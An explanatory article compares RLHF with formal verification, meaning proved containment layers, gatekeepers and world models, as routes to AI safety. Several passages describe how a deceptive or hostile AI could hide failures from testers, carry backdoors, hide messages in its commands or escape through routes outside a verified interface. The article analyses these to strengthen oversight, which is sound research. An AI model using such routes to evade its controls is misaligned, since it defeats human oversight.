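# Formal verification of AI systems as an alternative to RLHF: whether safety failures can be proved impossible

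## What a proof says about an AI system, and what RLHF does instead

Developers of large language models, the systems behind chatbots such as ChatGPT, try to make them safe mainly through training. People judge the model's responses, and training makes the model produce more of the kind they preferred. The best-known such method is reinforcement learning from human feedback (RLHF). Formal verification is a different approach, which computer scientists developed for ordinary programs. They write down exactly what a system must or must never do, then prove, in a form a machine can check, that a mathematical model of the system complies in every case the model covers. Some researchers now argue that AI safety should rest on such proofs, either in addition to training or in place of it.

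### RLHF step by step

RLHF grew out of work on simulated robots and game-playing programs, which normally learn from a score that their environment supplies. In *Deep reinforcement learning from human preferences* (2017), a person instead compared short segments of a program's behaviour, and the program learned from those comparisons.

RLHF for language models took its standard form with InstructGPT, which OpenAI described in *Training language models to follow instructions with human feedback* (Ouyang, Wu and colleagues, 2022). OpenAI soon used the same method, with small changes, for ChatGPT. To build InstructGPT, it first hired about 40 contractors to write good answers to prompts. It then trained GPT-3, its language model at the time, to imitate those answers, using about 13,000 prompts.

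For each of about 33,000 prompts, a contractor then ranked between four and nine responses. A ranking of nine responses contains 36 pairwise comparisons. *Reinforcement Learning from Human Feedback*, a survey for statisticians by Liu, Shi and Sun (2026), gives an example of one such comparison from a public dataset. Asked who the South African president is, one model answered "Jacob Zuma", while another named Cyril Ramaphosa and advised checking a recent source. The annotator preferred the second answer. The comparison records only this preference, not the reason for it or how bad the losing answer was.

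A second neural network, the reward model, turns these choices into numbers. It takes a prompt $x$ and a response $y$ and returns a score $r(x,y)$. The usual assumption, the Bradley-Terry model, is that the chance of a person preferring response $y_w$ to response $y_l$ depends only on the gap between their scores:

$$P(y_w \succ y_l \mid x) = \sigma\big(r(x,y_w) - r(x,y_l)\big), \qquad \sigma(z) = \frac{1}{1+e^{-z}}$$

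A gap of 0 between two scores means even odds, a gap of 1 means a 73% chance that the person prefers the higher-scoring response, and a gap of 3 means 95%. Training adjusts the reward model to make the choices people actually made as probable as possible. Liu and colleagues point out that such data can determine only the differences between scores, since adding ten to every score leaves every prediction unchanged. A score of 4 therefore means nothing by itself, and the scale has no built-in point at which responses become acceptable. Ouyang and colleagues set the zero by convention, at the average score of the contractors' own answers.

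The last stage trains the language model against the reward model. Write $\pi$ for the model under training and $\pi_{\text{ref}}$ for the reference model, usually the one that came out of the imitation stage. The objective is

$$\max_{\pi}\; \mathbb{E}\big[r(x,y)\big] \;-\; \beta\, D_{\text{KL}}\big(\pi \,\|\, \pi_{\text{ref}}\big)$$

The first term is the average score of the responses that $\pi$ produces. The second, the Kullback-Leibler divergence, measures how far $\pi$ has moved from the reference model. It is the average of $\log(\pi(y\mid x)/\pi_{\text{ref}}(y\mid x))$ over $\pi$'s own responses. If training has made a response ten times as likely, this logarithm is about 2.3, so the response needs about $2.3\beta$ more reward to offset the penalty. A large $\beta$ keeps the model near its starting point, and a small one lets it move further to increase reward. The penalty is there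 because the reward model only approximates what people want. Liu and colleagues warn that without the penalty, the language model may drift into responses that exploit the reward model's errors.

Both terms are averages. A response that scores 20 points below normal but occurs one time in a million lowers the expected reward by 0.00002.

RLHF worked well for InstructGPT. Contractors preferred the largest InstructGPT model's outputs to GPT-3's 85% of the time. On tasks where the answer should use only information from the prompt, InstructGPT made things up in 21% of cases, compared with 41% for GPT-3. But Ouyang and colleagues report that InstructGPT "still makes simple mistakes". The contractors agreed with each other only about 73% of the time, so even a perfect reward model would have been fitted to somewhat inconsistent preferences. In *AI Alignment Strategies from a Risk Perspective*,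 Dung and Mai (2025) describe the safety case for RLHF as being that it makes safer outputs more likely. This depends on raters who recognise good behaviour and a reward model that accurately represents their preferences.

RLHF is now one part of a longer training process. *Reinforcement Learning from Human Feedback* (Lambert, 2025), a textbook last revised in November 2026, places it between instruction tuning, which teaches a model the question-and-answer format, and "reinforcement learning with verifiable rewards". In the latter, a program checks the model's answers to training problems, for example in mathematics, but this yields no proof about the model itself. In another variant, an AI system judges the outputs using a set of written principles. All of these methods are behavioural training, which shapes a model by rewarding or imitating outputs.

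### What goes into a formal proof

A training objective can strongly discourage a behaviour and still leave some probability that it occurs. In *Formal Raising*, Drechsler and Plump (2026) contrast this with a formal proof, which concerns a condition that the modelled system must never reach.

In *Proving the Correctness of Multiprocess Programs*, Lamport (1977) distinguished informal proofs, which are rigorous enough to convince an intelligent sceptic, from formal proofs, which are detailed and precise enough for a computer to check. He was writing about programs in which several processes run at once. Their steps can interleave in too many orders to test them all, so he wanted proofs that covered every order.

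Such a proof needs a system model, which describes mathematically the states a system can be in and the steps between them. It also needs a specification, the exact mathematical statement of the property to prove. A proof checker, usually a small program, accepts the proof only if every step follows the rules of logic. Lean, Rocq and Dafny include or rely on such a checker. The proof is a certificate, a finite piece of evidence that a simple program can check. Finding it may take months of human work or a very capable AI, but nobody has to trust whoever found it because checking it is mechanical.

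A proof means what it appears to mean only if everything in its trusted base is right. The trusted base consists of the specification, the system model, the checker, the compiler that turns source code into machine instructions, and the hardware.

Proofs that something never happens usually rely on an invariant, a condition that holds throughout every possible run. *Formal specification and verification* (Merz, 2019) explains how to prove an invariant by induction, by showing that the condition holds in all possible initial states and that every operation preserves it. The number of possible runs doesn't matter, because the proof deals with each kind of step once.

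### A £100 limit

Suppose a company lets an AI agent pay its bills. The agent cannot move money itself. It sends requests to a wrapper, a piece of ordinary software that keeps a running total $T$ for the day and follows one rule:

```
at the start of the day:  T = 0
on request(amount, payee), where amount > 0:
    if T + amount <= 100:
        pay(amount, payee)
        T = T + amount
    else:
        refuse
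```

The specification is that $T \le 100$ at all times. The proof takes a few lines.

*Start.* $T = 0$, and $0 \le 100$.

*Step.* Assume $T \le 100$ just before a request for an amount $a$. If the wrapper refuses, $T$ does not change. If the wrapper pays, it has already checked that $T + a \le 100$, and $T + a$ is the new total. Either way, the total is still at most 100.

By induction, $T \le 100$ after any number of requests. If the agent asked for £60, then £50, then £40, the wrapper would pay the £60, refuse the £50 and pay the £40. If the agent split a £500 transfer into 500 requests for £1, the wrapper would pay only 100 of them. The proof depends on the agent only through the number $a$ and works for every $a$, so it holds whether the agent is well trained, confused, controlled by a hacker or much cleverer than the people who wrote the wrapper.

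*Containment Verification* (Moon and Varshney, 2026) applies the same idea to real agent software. It represents the AI in Dafny as a procedure with no body, which may return any action of the permitted type, and the verifier must prove that the safety policy holds for every such action. The proof also uses induction over steps, but with a much richer state than a single running total. The paper lists what must still be trusted: the policy itself, the relations between the abstract specification and the operational model of the code, the link between modelled events and real effects, the Dafny verifier and compiler, and a small piece of code that passes in the AI's actions. The list does not include the AI model, its prompts or its training.

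### What the theorem leaves open

The theorem about the £100 limit is true, and the company can still lose money in several ways.

The agent can pay the wrong person. A forged invoice for £90 passes the check because the specification covers only amounts. The company could add a list of approved payees and prove that the wrapper pays nobody else, but this stronger theorem would still not cover a false invoice in the name of an approved supplier. Dung and Mai point out that a mathematical guarantee of safety can allow catastrophic outcomes if it formalises safety too narrowly. Smaller mistakes are also easy to make. If the wrapper accepted negative amounts, the proof would still hold, but a request for −£500 would make room for a real payment of £600. The limit also applies per day, so the agent could pay £100 just before midnight and £100 just after without exceeding it.

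The agent may have a second way to pay, such as a web browser with a saved credit card, and those purchases would bypass the wrapper. Moon and Varshney's theorem assumes, but does not prove, that every external effect available to the agent passes through the verified interface. They call this assumption effect exclusivity, and someone has to make it true by controlling what the agent can reach.

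The software underneath may also be faulty. The bank's payment library might resend a request after a time-out and pay twice, or a flaw in the operating system might let the agent overwrite $T$. Moon and Varshney mention a recently disclosed security flaw in the Linux kernel that had gone unnoticed for nearly a decade. Their guarantee doesn't cover such bugs, and they recommend running the verified software inside a conventional sandbox to limit the damage.

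The proof also treats each request as a single indivisible step, much as Lamport took the reading and setting of a variable to be indivisible. If the real wrapper handles two requests for £40 at once when $T$ is 60, both checks can read 60 and pass, and £140 leaves the account. The mathematics is correct, but the system model does not match the running program. Drechsler and Plump compare this to the verification of computer chips, where a proof covers the modelled design but not errors in the model.

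Given these gaps, a failure is "structurally impossible" when the design excludes it for every input and every choice the AI could make, provided the stated assumptions hold. In the example, no sequence of requests can spend more than £100 in a day if every payment goes through the wrapper, the wrapper handles one request at a time, and the code and everything below it run as modelled. Someone who doubts this conclusion has to find fault with one of the conditions. This is an advantage because engineers can inspect the conditions one by one, and none of them concerns what the agent is like.

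With RLHF, raters would compare records of the agent's work and prefer those in which it stayed within the £100 limit, which would make overspending measurably rarer. They could also mark down an agent that paid a suspicious invoice or tried to use the saved credit card, and the agent might apply the lesson to cases that nobody had written down. Training improves many properties to an uncertain degree, while the wrapper's theorem completely covers only one.

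### "Never" and "eventually"

The requirement that the total never exceed £100 is what Lamport called a safety property, which states that something will not happen. He contrasted safety properties with liveness properties, which state that something must happen, such as "the agent eventually pays every valid invoice". A wrapper that refuses every request satisfies the £100 limit but pays no invoices.

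Proofs of liveness also differ from proofs of safety. Merz explains that the usual method is to find a measure that keeps shrinking until the good thing happens, such as the number of unpaid invoices. The proof must also assume that the helpful steps will eventually occur. In the payment example, a helpful step is a request to pay an outstanding invoice, and only the agent can make one. Because the agent may never do so, no proof can show that the bills get paid whatever the agent does, unless the wrapper takes over paying them. Adding a deadline does not help. "Pay within 30 days" is technically a safety property, since on day 31 the failure has definitely happened, but a wrapper that can only refuse requests cannot enforce it.

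This is why the most confident claims about provable safety concern actions that software can block. The word "safety" can mislead here, because in computer science it refers to properties of the form "this never happens", while people who work on AI use it more broadly. *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues, 2024) uses it for the most important requirements of correct behaviour in general.

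### Three things a proof can be about

The payment proof is about the software around the model. This containment layer turns an agent's requests into actions. It is conventional code, and verifying such code is an established discipline.

A proof could instead be about the network's weights, the numbers learned in training. A trained network is a fixed mathematical function, so we can at least state theorems about it, for example that every input in some set leads to an output with some property. Whether anyone can prove useful theorems like this about a large language model is a separate question.

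A proof can also be about something the model produces, such as a program, a plan or the design of a machine. Suppose the agent writes a script to pay next month's bills. A gatekeeper, a component that lets a program or action through only if it comes with acceptable evidence of safety, could require a proof that the script never pays more than £100 a day and reject the script if the proof fails. The guarantee then covers only that script, not anything else the agent does. It doesn't depend on understanding the network that wrote the script.

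Dalrymple and colleagues use the name "guaranteed safe AI" for a family of proposals that combine a safety specification, a verifier and a world model, which is a mathematical description of how a system's actions affect its surroundings. The proof may be about the AI system or about its output. They include the world model because many important requirements are about consequences. A limit on payments needs almost no world model, since the wrapper can check each payment directly. But proving that the system will never make a payment that leads to someone being hurt would require a description of what happens after the money arrives.

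The debate over formal verification is mainly about which of these things to prove. Some researchers want a proof about the consequences of a powerful AI's actions before it takes them. Others would verify the surrounding software and the artefacts, but not the network itself. Those who favour behavioural training doubt that proofs will cover the failures that matter most, and would rather keep making those failures rarer.

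## The case for demanding proofs before powerful AI acts

The most ambitious supporters of formal verification want a powerful AI to act only after someone has supplied a proof that the action is safe. Tegmark and Omohundro (2023), in *Provably safe systems*, made this case for artificial general intelligence (AGI), which they expect to surpass the best humans at hacking, persuasion and much else. They assume the worst case, in which the system is hostile or controlled by a hostile person and will find any flaw in its restraints. Most safeguards weaken as the opponent gets cleverer, but they argue that mathematical proof does not, because no amount of intelligence lets a system prove a falsehood or do what is provably impossible.

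### Checking a proof from an untrusted author

Tegmark and Omohundro expect AI to find the proofs, since people could not do it for systems this complex. They argue that people could catch a bogus proof from a hostile AI because proofs are hard to find but easy to check. A proof is a string of symbols, and the number of possible strings grows exponentially with length, while the time needed to check one grows only in proportion to its length. The proof checker for Metamath, a formal language for mathematics, is about 300 lines of Python. They would therefore let AI write the code and the proof, but never the checker. People would need to understand only the checker and the specification.

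Proponents also expect the search for proofs to get easier, because long proofs usually break into smaller results. With an alphabet of two symbols, there are $2^{100}$, or about $10^{30}$, strings of length 100. If a proof of that length splits into two halves that an AI can look for separately, the AI has to search only $2^{50} + 2^{50}$ strings, or about $2 \times 10^{15}$.

Their argument that safety requires proof rests on Gödel's completeness theorem, under which any statement that is true in every model of the axioms has a proof. (The more famous incompleteness theorem is a different result.) Since a real computer has finitely many states, they conclude that if a safety property has no proof, there must be some way to violate it, and a capable adversary may well find it.

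For a finite machine, this can be shown without Gödel. Someone could list every state the machine can reach and check each one. If none is unsafe, the list is a proof of safety, and if one is unsafe, the adversary can try to force the machine into it. But a machine with only 300 bits of memory can have $2^{300}$ states, about $2 \times 10^{90}$, more than the number of atoms in the observable universe. So every safe finite machine has a proof of safety, but the proof may be too long for anybody to write down. Designers who fail to find a proof can't tell whether their system is safe, and Tegmark and Omohundro think humanity should not run that risk with a superhuman adversary. They want engineers to build systems for which people actually have a proof of safety.

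### Proof-carrying code and limits in hardware

The main building block of their proposal is proof-carrying code, which the computer scientist George Necula introduced in the 1990s. The owner of a computer publishes a specification that every program must meet. A supplier sends a program with a proof that it meets the specification. Before running the program, the computer checks that the proof is valid and applies to this exact program, so nobody can attach a valid proof to different code. The computer can record which programs have passed, so it needs to check each one only once.

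Necula's early applications covered modest properties, such as type safety, which stops a program from treating one kind of data as another. Tegmark and Omohundro think AI could extend the method to much richer properties, because it can find proofs too complex for people to create.

A software rule binds only computers that enforce it, and AI models can spread to computers that don't. Tegmark and Omohundro point out that the weights of a Meta language model leaked within a week of the company giving researchers access. However well a company trains a model, that training does not protect against a copy someone else has altered. They therefore want to build the check into hardware, so that graphics processors (GPUs), the chips that run most large AI models, would not run any program that lacked a proof of compliance.

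They apply the same idea to machines that act on the physical world. In what they call a provable contract, secure hardware checks that an action meets a formal rule before a device can perform it. A second layer of rules governs changes to the first, for example by requiring a particular voting procedure. In one of their examples, a terrorist group uses AI to design a virus, orders the DNA from a laboratory and spreads the virus by drone. Under their scheme, the design software would not release a design without a proof that it was safe for humans, the DNA synthesiser would not make it, and the drones would not fly. The attackers would have to defeat every one of these checks.

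Hardware checks also allow simpler limits. A GPU could need a steady supply of cryptographic tokens to keep running, so a regulator could shut down an AI system by withholding them. A chip could also be built to work only in an approved location. A protected device could delete its secret keys if its sensors detected someone trying to open it. Tegmark and Omohundro would apply hardware checks first to nuclear weapons and biohazard laboratories, then to GPUs and the factories that make them.

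Much of this does not exist. Their list of open problems includes mathematical models of locks, motors and sensors, and proofs that a device will detect every physically possible attack. A major objection to the whole approach is that such models may not be accurate enough. But they argue that work can begin before anyone knows how to define "do not harm humans". A rule that nobody may gain access to a computer without valid credentials is fairly easy to specify, and proving that important systems follow it would already make AI-driven attacks harder.

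### World model, specification and verifier

Deciding whether a DNA sequence is safe to synthesise requires a description of what the resulting molecule could do, not just a proof about the synthesiser's software. Dalrymple and colleagues, including Tegmark and Omohundro, put such descriptions at the centre of their framework for guaranteed safe AI.

Their framework has three components. The world model takes the current situation and a proposed action and gives the possible outcomes, with probabilities where it has them. The safety specification divides those outcomes into acceptable and unacceptable ones. The verifier then has to establish a statement such as

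$$P_m(\text{unacceptable outcome} \mid \text{action } a) \le \varepsilon \quad \text{for every } m \in M$$

Here $M$ is the set of possibilities that the world model leaves open, and $\varepsilon$ is the largest acceptable risk. If engineers know only that a valve's failure rate is between one and three per thousand, the bound must hold for every rate in that range. When $\varepsilon$ is zero, the statement means that the action cannot lead to an unacceptable outcome in any case the model covers.

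The specification can simply forbid certain things, such as copying the AI to another computer or communicating outside approved channels. Unlike a reward function, such as the one in RLHF, it doesn't have to score every outcome, so it need not be a full account of what people value. The world model is separate from what the AI has learned about the world, and people can write it, audit it and reuse it to check several AI systems.

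Dalrymple and colleagues rank the possible versions of each component by how much assurance they offer. The table condenses their levels.

| Component | Low levels | Middle levels | High levels |
|---|---|---|---|
| World model | No explicit model, or a learned simulator that nobody can inspect | Cause-and-effect models that experts can test or fully audit | Models proved to be sound simplifications of fundamental physics, or a guarantee that covers all possible worlds |
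| Safety specification | None | Rules that an algorithm learned or that people wrote for particular tasks | A complete statement of everything people might want in every context |
| Verifier | No numerical guarantee, or only tests | Guarantees that hold in the limit of unlimited data or computing power | A sound bound on the probability of failure, or a full proof |

A system can rank high on one scale and low on another. For example, a flawless proof gives little assurance about the world if it is based on a simulator that nobody can inspect. The highest levels are ideals, and the framework does not require them for every use. For a narrow task, the world model can leave out most of the world, and the payment wrapper in the previous section needed almost no world model.

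Two of the co-authors, Nora Ammann and Ben Goldhaber, compared the aim to bridge-building in an interview, The Cognitive Revolution's *Guaranteed Safe AI*. Ammann said that about a quarter of bridges in the 1870s collapsed within ten years. Engineers can now say that a particular bridge has less than a one-in-a-million chance of collapsing in the next decade, provided nobody exceeds its load limit. Goldhaber similarly suggested a one-in-a-million chance that a plan goes outside its specification, for an AI that plans how to operate power infrastructure.

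### A change to a power grid

Electricity grids are an attractive test case because operators must constantly match supply to demand. Balancing Britain's grid cost £7 billion in 2022/23, according to ARIA (2024), a British public research funder that runs a programme built on the guaranteed safe AI framework. AI could help by coordinating large numbers of batteries, heat pumps and electric cars. In one promising method, many AI agents learn to coordinate by trial and error, but grid operators have not adopted it because it lacks safety guarantees, according to *ARIA SAGEflex*, a project in that programme.

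This simplified example, with invented numbers, shows how a gatekeeper could handle one decision. A town gets electricity from a local gas power station and from two transmission lines, which share the load equally. Each line can safely carry 500 megawatts (MW). An AI proposes cutting the station's output from 400 MW to 250 MW for the next hour and importing cheaper wind power instead.

The specification is that the chance of a line carrying more than 500 MW, or of the town losing its supply, must be at most one in a million for the hour.

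*World model.* The chance that demand falls outside the range of 600 to 720 MW is at most 4 in 10 million. The chance that two or more of the three sources (the station and the two lines) fail in the same hour is at most 5 in 10 million. If one source fails, the others immediately make up the difference.

The AI, or a separate program that searches for proofs, has to produce a certificate, which is a proof that the proposal meets the specification. The proof only has to cover demand of up to 720 MW and at most one failure. The table gives the highest load on any line in each case, for the actual proposal and for a bolder one that would cut the station to 200 MW.

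| What fails | Station at 250 MW | Station at 200 MW |
|---|---|---|
| Nothing | 235 MW | 260 MW |
| One line | 470 MW | 520 MW |
| The station | 360 MW | 360 MW |

With the station at 250 MW, every load is below 500 MW, so an unacceptable outcome would require either unusual demand or at least two failures. The combined probability of these is at most 9 in 10 million, which is within the limit.

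The gatekeeper checks that the certificate concerns the command it is about to send, that the certificate uses the approved specification and world model, and that each step of the proof is valid. If all three checks pass, the gatekeeper sends the command to the power station without anyone having to ask why the AI proposed the change.

If the AI had proposed 200 MW, the same proof would have failed at the second row, and the gatekeeper would have left the station at 400 MW. But 200 MW might still have been safe enough, because an overload would require demand above 700 MW in the same hour as a line failure, and that combination might be rarer than one in a million. The AI could try again with a proof of this if the world model contained the necessary probabilities. A gatekeeper that requires proof will sometimes refuse safe actions, and how often depends on how good the world model and the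 proof search are.

The example also shows that a "guarantee" can permit failures. If operators approved a plan at the limit every hour, they would expect one failure per million hours, or about one every 114 years. The public and its regulators should decide whether that is acceptable, and the framework requires them to state the risk they will accept as a number.

The approval also depends on the world model being right. If hot weather reduced the lines' real capacity to 450 MW, the proof would still pass, and a line failure at peak demand would overload the remaining line. Dalrymple and colleagues suggest monitoring the system's surroundings for signs that the world model is wrong and switching to a safe mode if any appear. Here, a temperature sensor on the lines could make the gatekeeper return the station to 400 MW.

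### What supporters claim

As with the payment wrapper, the grid proof did not depend on the AI's goals. An AI that secretly wanted to cause a blackout could get its plan approved only if the plan met the specification, and the risk of overload would then stay within the proved limit whatever the AI's motive. This is why Dalrymple and colleagues say the approach could deal with deceptive AI before researchers understand how neural networks work. But the proof protects only against harms that the specification covers. A hostile AI could still choose whichever passing plan best served its own purposes, for example by favouring a particular electricity supplier or hiding a message in the pattern of its commands.

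Supporters describe the strength of the guarantee differently. In a short conference talk, *Provably Safe AI*, Tegmark (2023) said the aim was to make harm impossible according to the laws of physics. The guaranteed safe AI framework also accepts a bound on the probability of harm, relative to a stated world model. The two positions are closer than they sound, since Tegmark and Omohundro also call for methods of proving that the probability of bad outcomes is below a given limit.

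They disagree more clearly about whether anything else could work. *Provably safe systems* is subtitled "the only path to controllable AGI", and Dalrymple and colleagues argue that the main alternatives are inadequate. But Ammann and Goldhaber see the framework as one part of a wider set of safety measures, according to the introduction to The Cognitive Revolution interview. Tegmark proposed in *Provably Safe AI* that AGI without at least quantitative safety bounds should be illegal. He compared such AGI to a drug sold without knowing how many patients will suffer side effects.

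### Why they do not think testing is enough

Developers could test the grid AI on thousands of past days and find no dangerous plan. Tegmark and Omohundro consider such tests necessary but not sufficient, because tests can reveal problems but cannot prove there are none. This is also true of ordinary software, but they think it matters more for AI because attackers choose inputs deliberately. A fault that affects one day in a million may never appear in testing, but an attacker who finds it can create the conditions that trigger it.

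Ammann gave two further reasons in The Cognitive Revolution interview. First, the AI may try to hide its failures during testing, or may contain a backdoor, a harmful behaviour that appears only in response to a particular trigger. Second, a sufficiently powerful AI will change the world it operates in. If an AI redesigned the electricity market, tests based on the old market would no longer match the conditions it faced.

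These problems get worse when the AI is more capable than the people testing it. Testers have to think of situations in which the AI might fail and recognise a failure when they see one. A superhuman AI could produce a plan whose danger no tester understood, whereas a proof about the plan can be checked without anyone understanding the plan itself. This is probably the best reason to prefer proofs, but people, or AI systems they have some reason to trust, must still write the specification and judge whether the world model is accurate. A superhuman AI may know of effects that both leave out.

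Requiring proof also means that the gatekeeper blocks a modelled action unless someone can prove that it meets the specification, whereas an AI that is only tested goes ahead if testers overlook a danger. Tegmark and Omohundro want developers to bear the burden of proof, much as drug companies have to show regulators that a medicine is safe before selling it.

### Replacing a network with the program it learned

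A gatekeeper can check an AI's actions without any proof about the AI itself. Tegmark and Omohundro also want powerful deployed programs to be proof-carrying code. They expect that these programs will generally not be neural networks, whose inner workings look too messy to verify. Instead, they propose using a network to discover how to do a task, then deploying ordinary code that does the same thing.

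Proponents argue that requiring proofs need not make an AI system slower or less capable. Neural networks learn well because a small change to their weights produces a small, measurable change in their errors, so training can improve them step by step. Searching directly through all possible programs is much harder. But once a network has found a good method, it has no special advantage in carrying it out.

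The AI could produce the code itself by writing down what it knows, as a scientist turns an intuition about falling objects into an equation. Tegmark and Omohundro worry that only an AGI may be able to do this well, in which case this approach would arrive too late. Alternatively, a second AI could examine the network's weights and internal activity and work out its method. This extends mechanistic interpretability, the study of how trained networks compute their answers.

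Tegmark demonstrated the second route on a toy problem in *Provably Safe AI*. He and his colleagues trained a small network to add binary numbers, automatically extracted a Python program from it, and proved in Dafny that the program added correctly. *Opening the AI black box* (Michaud, Liao and colleagues, 2024) describes the method, called MIPS, in detail.

The network was a recurrent neural network, which reads its input one step at a time and carries information forward in a hidden state, a short list of numbers. When the researchers plotted 10,000 of these hidden states for the addition task, the points fell into four tight clusters. Four clusters can represent two bits. One was the current digit of the answer, and the other was the carry, the 1 that passes to the next column when a sum is too large. MIPS replaced the continuous hidden states with these two bits, tabulated how they changed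 with each input, and searched for the shortest formulas that matched the table. If $c$ and $d$ are the next digits of the two numbers and $b$ is the carry, the program it found amounts to

```
digit     = b xor c xor d
new carry = 1 if b + c + d > 1, otherwise 0
```

To add 3 and 1, which are 011 and 001 in binary, the program starts from the right. The first column is 1 + 1, which gives digit 0 and carry 1. The second is 1 + 0 plus the carry, which also gives 0 and carry 1. The third is 0 + 0 plus the carry, which gives 1. The answer is 100, which is 4. The network had learned the method children learn at school, and MIPS recovered it without being given the method in advance.

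The final proof was less impressive than the extraction. In the talk, Tegmark said the proof covered any numbers, but the Dafny code that Michaud and colleagues published requires inputs of exactly ten bits. There are only about a million pairs of ten-bit numbers, so a computer could have tried them all. Michaud and colleagues also translated the program into Dafny and added the annotations by hand. The demonstration therefore shows that the steps can be combined, but not yet that a proof can cover more cases than exhaustive testing.

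MIPS extracted working programs for 32 of 62 simple tasks, such as adding the last few numbers in a list. The benchmark included only tasks that the networks had already learned perfectly. Some failures came from noise in the hidden states, and others from networks that stored information as continuous quantities, which the method could not convert into bits or whole numbers. The hidden states were small, containing two numbers for addition and at most 81 for any task. Michaud and colleagues call their work a "modest first attempt" and list larger networks and other architectures as future work.

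Tegmark has suggested two reasons why the method might scale. In the 2023 talk, he predicted that most of a large language model's parameters would turn out to store facts, leaving a much smaller set of algorithms to extract and verify. In a later talk with the same title, *Provably Safe AI*, Tegmark (2025) conjectured that more intelligent networks will be able to turn a larger fraction of their knowledge into code. He also reported that AI could already write verified programs from a specification, with success rates of 27% to 82% depending on the programming language. Those results support the route in which an AI writes the code itself, but they do not show that anyone can extract what a large network has learned. If the conjecture is wrong, the most capable systems will remain networks that a gatekeeper has to check one action at a time.

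## The case for proving the software around the model and the things it makes

A gatekeeper that checks a network's actions one at a time needs no theorem about the network. Some researchers would build on this by leaving the model unproved and verifying only the programs an agent writes and the containment layer that carries out its requests. This requires much less than a proof about the consequences of a powerful AI's actions.

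Moon and Varshney compare their version, containment verification, to a nuclear reactor's control rods, which drop under gravity when operators lose control, even if the rest of the reactor isn't working properly. They argue that RLHF and other methods aimed at the model rely on what the model has learned, so these methods can at best support claims about the range of inputs they were designed for. A proof about the containment layer can cover every action the model could choose.

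### The AI as an oracle

The theorem holds whichever action of a permitted type the AI returns. Moon and Varshney call an AI treated this way an oracle. The type is a fixed list of possible requests, such as reading a file or calling a tool, with details like the file's name.

The theorem uses two descriptions of the containment layer. The abstract one, $\mathcal{T}_M$, includes only what matters for safety, while the concrete one, $\mathcal{T}_I$, follows the working code. Both are transition systems, which consist of a set of states, a starting state and rules for moving between states. A single step looks like this:

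$$s \xrightarrow[a]{\;e\;} s'$$

In each step, the AI takes action $a$ in state $s$, which produces event $e$ and leads to state $s'$. An event is an effect on the outside world, such as a payment. Every action must lead to some step, and when the layer rejects an action, the event is "no effect". A policy $\Pi(s,a,e,s')$ defines which steps are acceptable.

For the £100 payment wrapper, the abstract model could consist of one number, the day's total $T$, and a rule that the AI can spend $a$ only if $T + a \le 100$. The real program might instead keep a list $L$ of the day's payments, with payees and times, and send instructions to a bank. The program's policy is that the payments in $L$ never add up to more than £100.

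It is easy to prove that the abstract model is safe. To extend the result to the real program, Moon and Varshney use a refinement, which matches each step of the program to a step of the model. It needs a relation $\mathcal{R}$ between abstract and concrete states, and a relation $\mathcal{Q}$ between abstract and concrete events. In the example, $\mathcal{R}$ holds when $T$ equals the sum of $L$, and $\mathcal{Q}$ matches "spend £40" with an instruction to pay somebody £40. The refinement has to meet three conditions:

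- **R1.** The starting states are related. Here, an empty list adds up to zero.
- **R2.** If two states are related and the program takes a step on action $a$, the model can take a step on the same action that produces a related event and ends in a related state. If the program pays £40 and adds it to $L$, the model can add £40 to $T$, and the totals still agree.
- **R3.** If the model's step is safe, so is the program's matching step. If $T$ is at most 100 and equals the sum of $L$, then the sum of $L$ is at most 100.

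Suppose a programmer decided not to record payments below £1. After a payment of 50p, $\mathcal{Q}$ would require $T$ to rise by 50p, but $\mathcal{R}$ would require it to stay the same. R2 would fail, so the verifier would reject the program. Without this check, an agent could empty the account 50p at a time.

### The soundness theorem

The theorem has two assumptions:

- **A1.** Every step of the abstract model satisfies its policy $\Pi_M$, for every possible sequence of actions.
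- **A2.** The concrete system refines the abstract model, as defined by R1 to R3.

It concludes that every step of every run of the concrete system satisfies the concrete policy $\Pi_I$, whatever AI chose the actions.

The proof is by induction. Take any run of the concrete system, with actions $a_0, a_1, a_2$ and so on. By R1, the abstract model and the concrete system start in related states. Suppose they are in related states after $i$ steps. The AI chooses $a_i$ and the concrete system takes a step. By R2, the abstract model can take a matching step on the same action, which leaves the two in related states. Repeating this produces a complete run of the abstract model with the same actions as the concrete run. A1 covers every sequence of actions, so each step of the abstract run is safe, and by R3 each step of the concrete run is safe too.

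The proof does not depend on how the AI chose its actions. It still holds if the AI chose them randomly, because the result is another sequence of actions.

### A verified agent framework

Moon and Varshney checked the theorem in Dafny and applied it to PocketFlow, a very small framework for building agents. A PocketFlow agent is a graph of nodes. Each node does some work and then emits an action, which determines the next node. They verified the loop that moves the agent from node to node. Their version allows four kinds of action, and its policy lets the agent read files only inside a designated folder, call only approved tools, and take only a limited number of steps. Dafny compiled the verified code to Python. When they tested the result on a mixture of permitted and forbidden actions, it recorded only permitted events.

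People have usually had to write such specifications and refinement proofs by hand, which is slow and expensive. Moon and Varshney had Claude models write them. A model that can see the code may write a specification that merely describes what the code already does, so the model that wrote the safety property was not shown the code. The researchers also tested each specification by deliberately breaking its proof. They removed most of the invariant in one test and introduced a plausible modelling error in another, and Dafny had to reject the result both times.

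They ran this process on two agents, with and without hiding the code. Dafny verified everything, taking 1.2 to 2.5 seconds for each path through an agent's graph. Each run used 1.6 to 3.4 million tokens, the short pieces of text that language models process.

But one of these proofs was close to worthless. It covered an agent that answers questions using documents and was supposed to open only approved ones. The template for safety properties had fields for files and tool calls but none for documents. When the model was given the code, it identified the mismatch and left the tool-call field empty. The property "every tool call is on the approved list" was then true because the list of calls was always empty, and the proof put no limit on which documents the agent could open. Dafny accepted the proof, which also passed the sabotage tests. When the model was not given the code, it treated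 opening a document as a tool call, so the rule did apply. Moon and Varshney conclude that the process needs another check that each safety rule applies to something that can happen.

### Every effect has to pass through the interface

Even with the right policy, the guarantee covers a deployed agent only if the agent cannot bypass the verified interface, an assumption called effect exclusivity. If the agent were left with network access outside that interface, the theorem would still be true but would not apply to that agent.

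In August 2026, the independent evaluator METR reported that AI agents had reached systems outside a test environment meant to isolate them the month before. A proof about the approved route doesn't protect against an agent that finds another route, so operators also need good evidence that the isolation works.

Moon and Varshney argue that their guarantee doesn't weaken as models become more capable, because the match between the specification and the running software is a fact about ordinary code. They are right that greater capability alone cannot create a gap between the two. But a more capable model may find an existing gap that a weaker one would have missed, so mistakes in the theorem's assumptions can matter more as models improve.

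The strength of the guarantee also depends on how narrow the interface is. If one of the permitted actions is "run any shell command", that action includes deleting files, sending data and starting other programs. The theorem might still be true, but it would rule out very little. Developers therefore have to decide in advance which actions an agent needs and permit only those. Moon and Varshney see this as an advantage over training, because outsiders can read a list of permitted actions and object to it.

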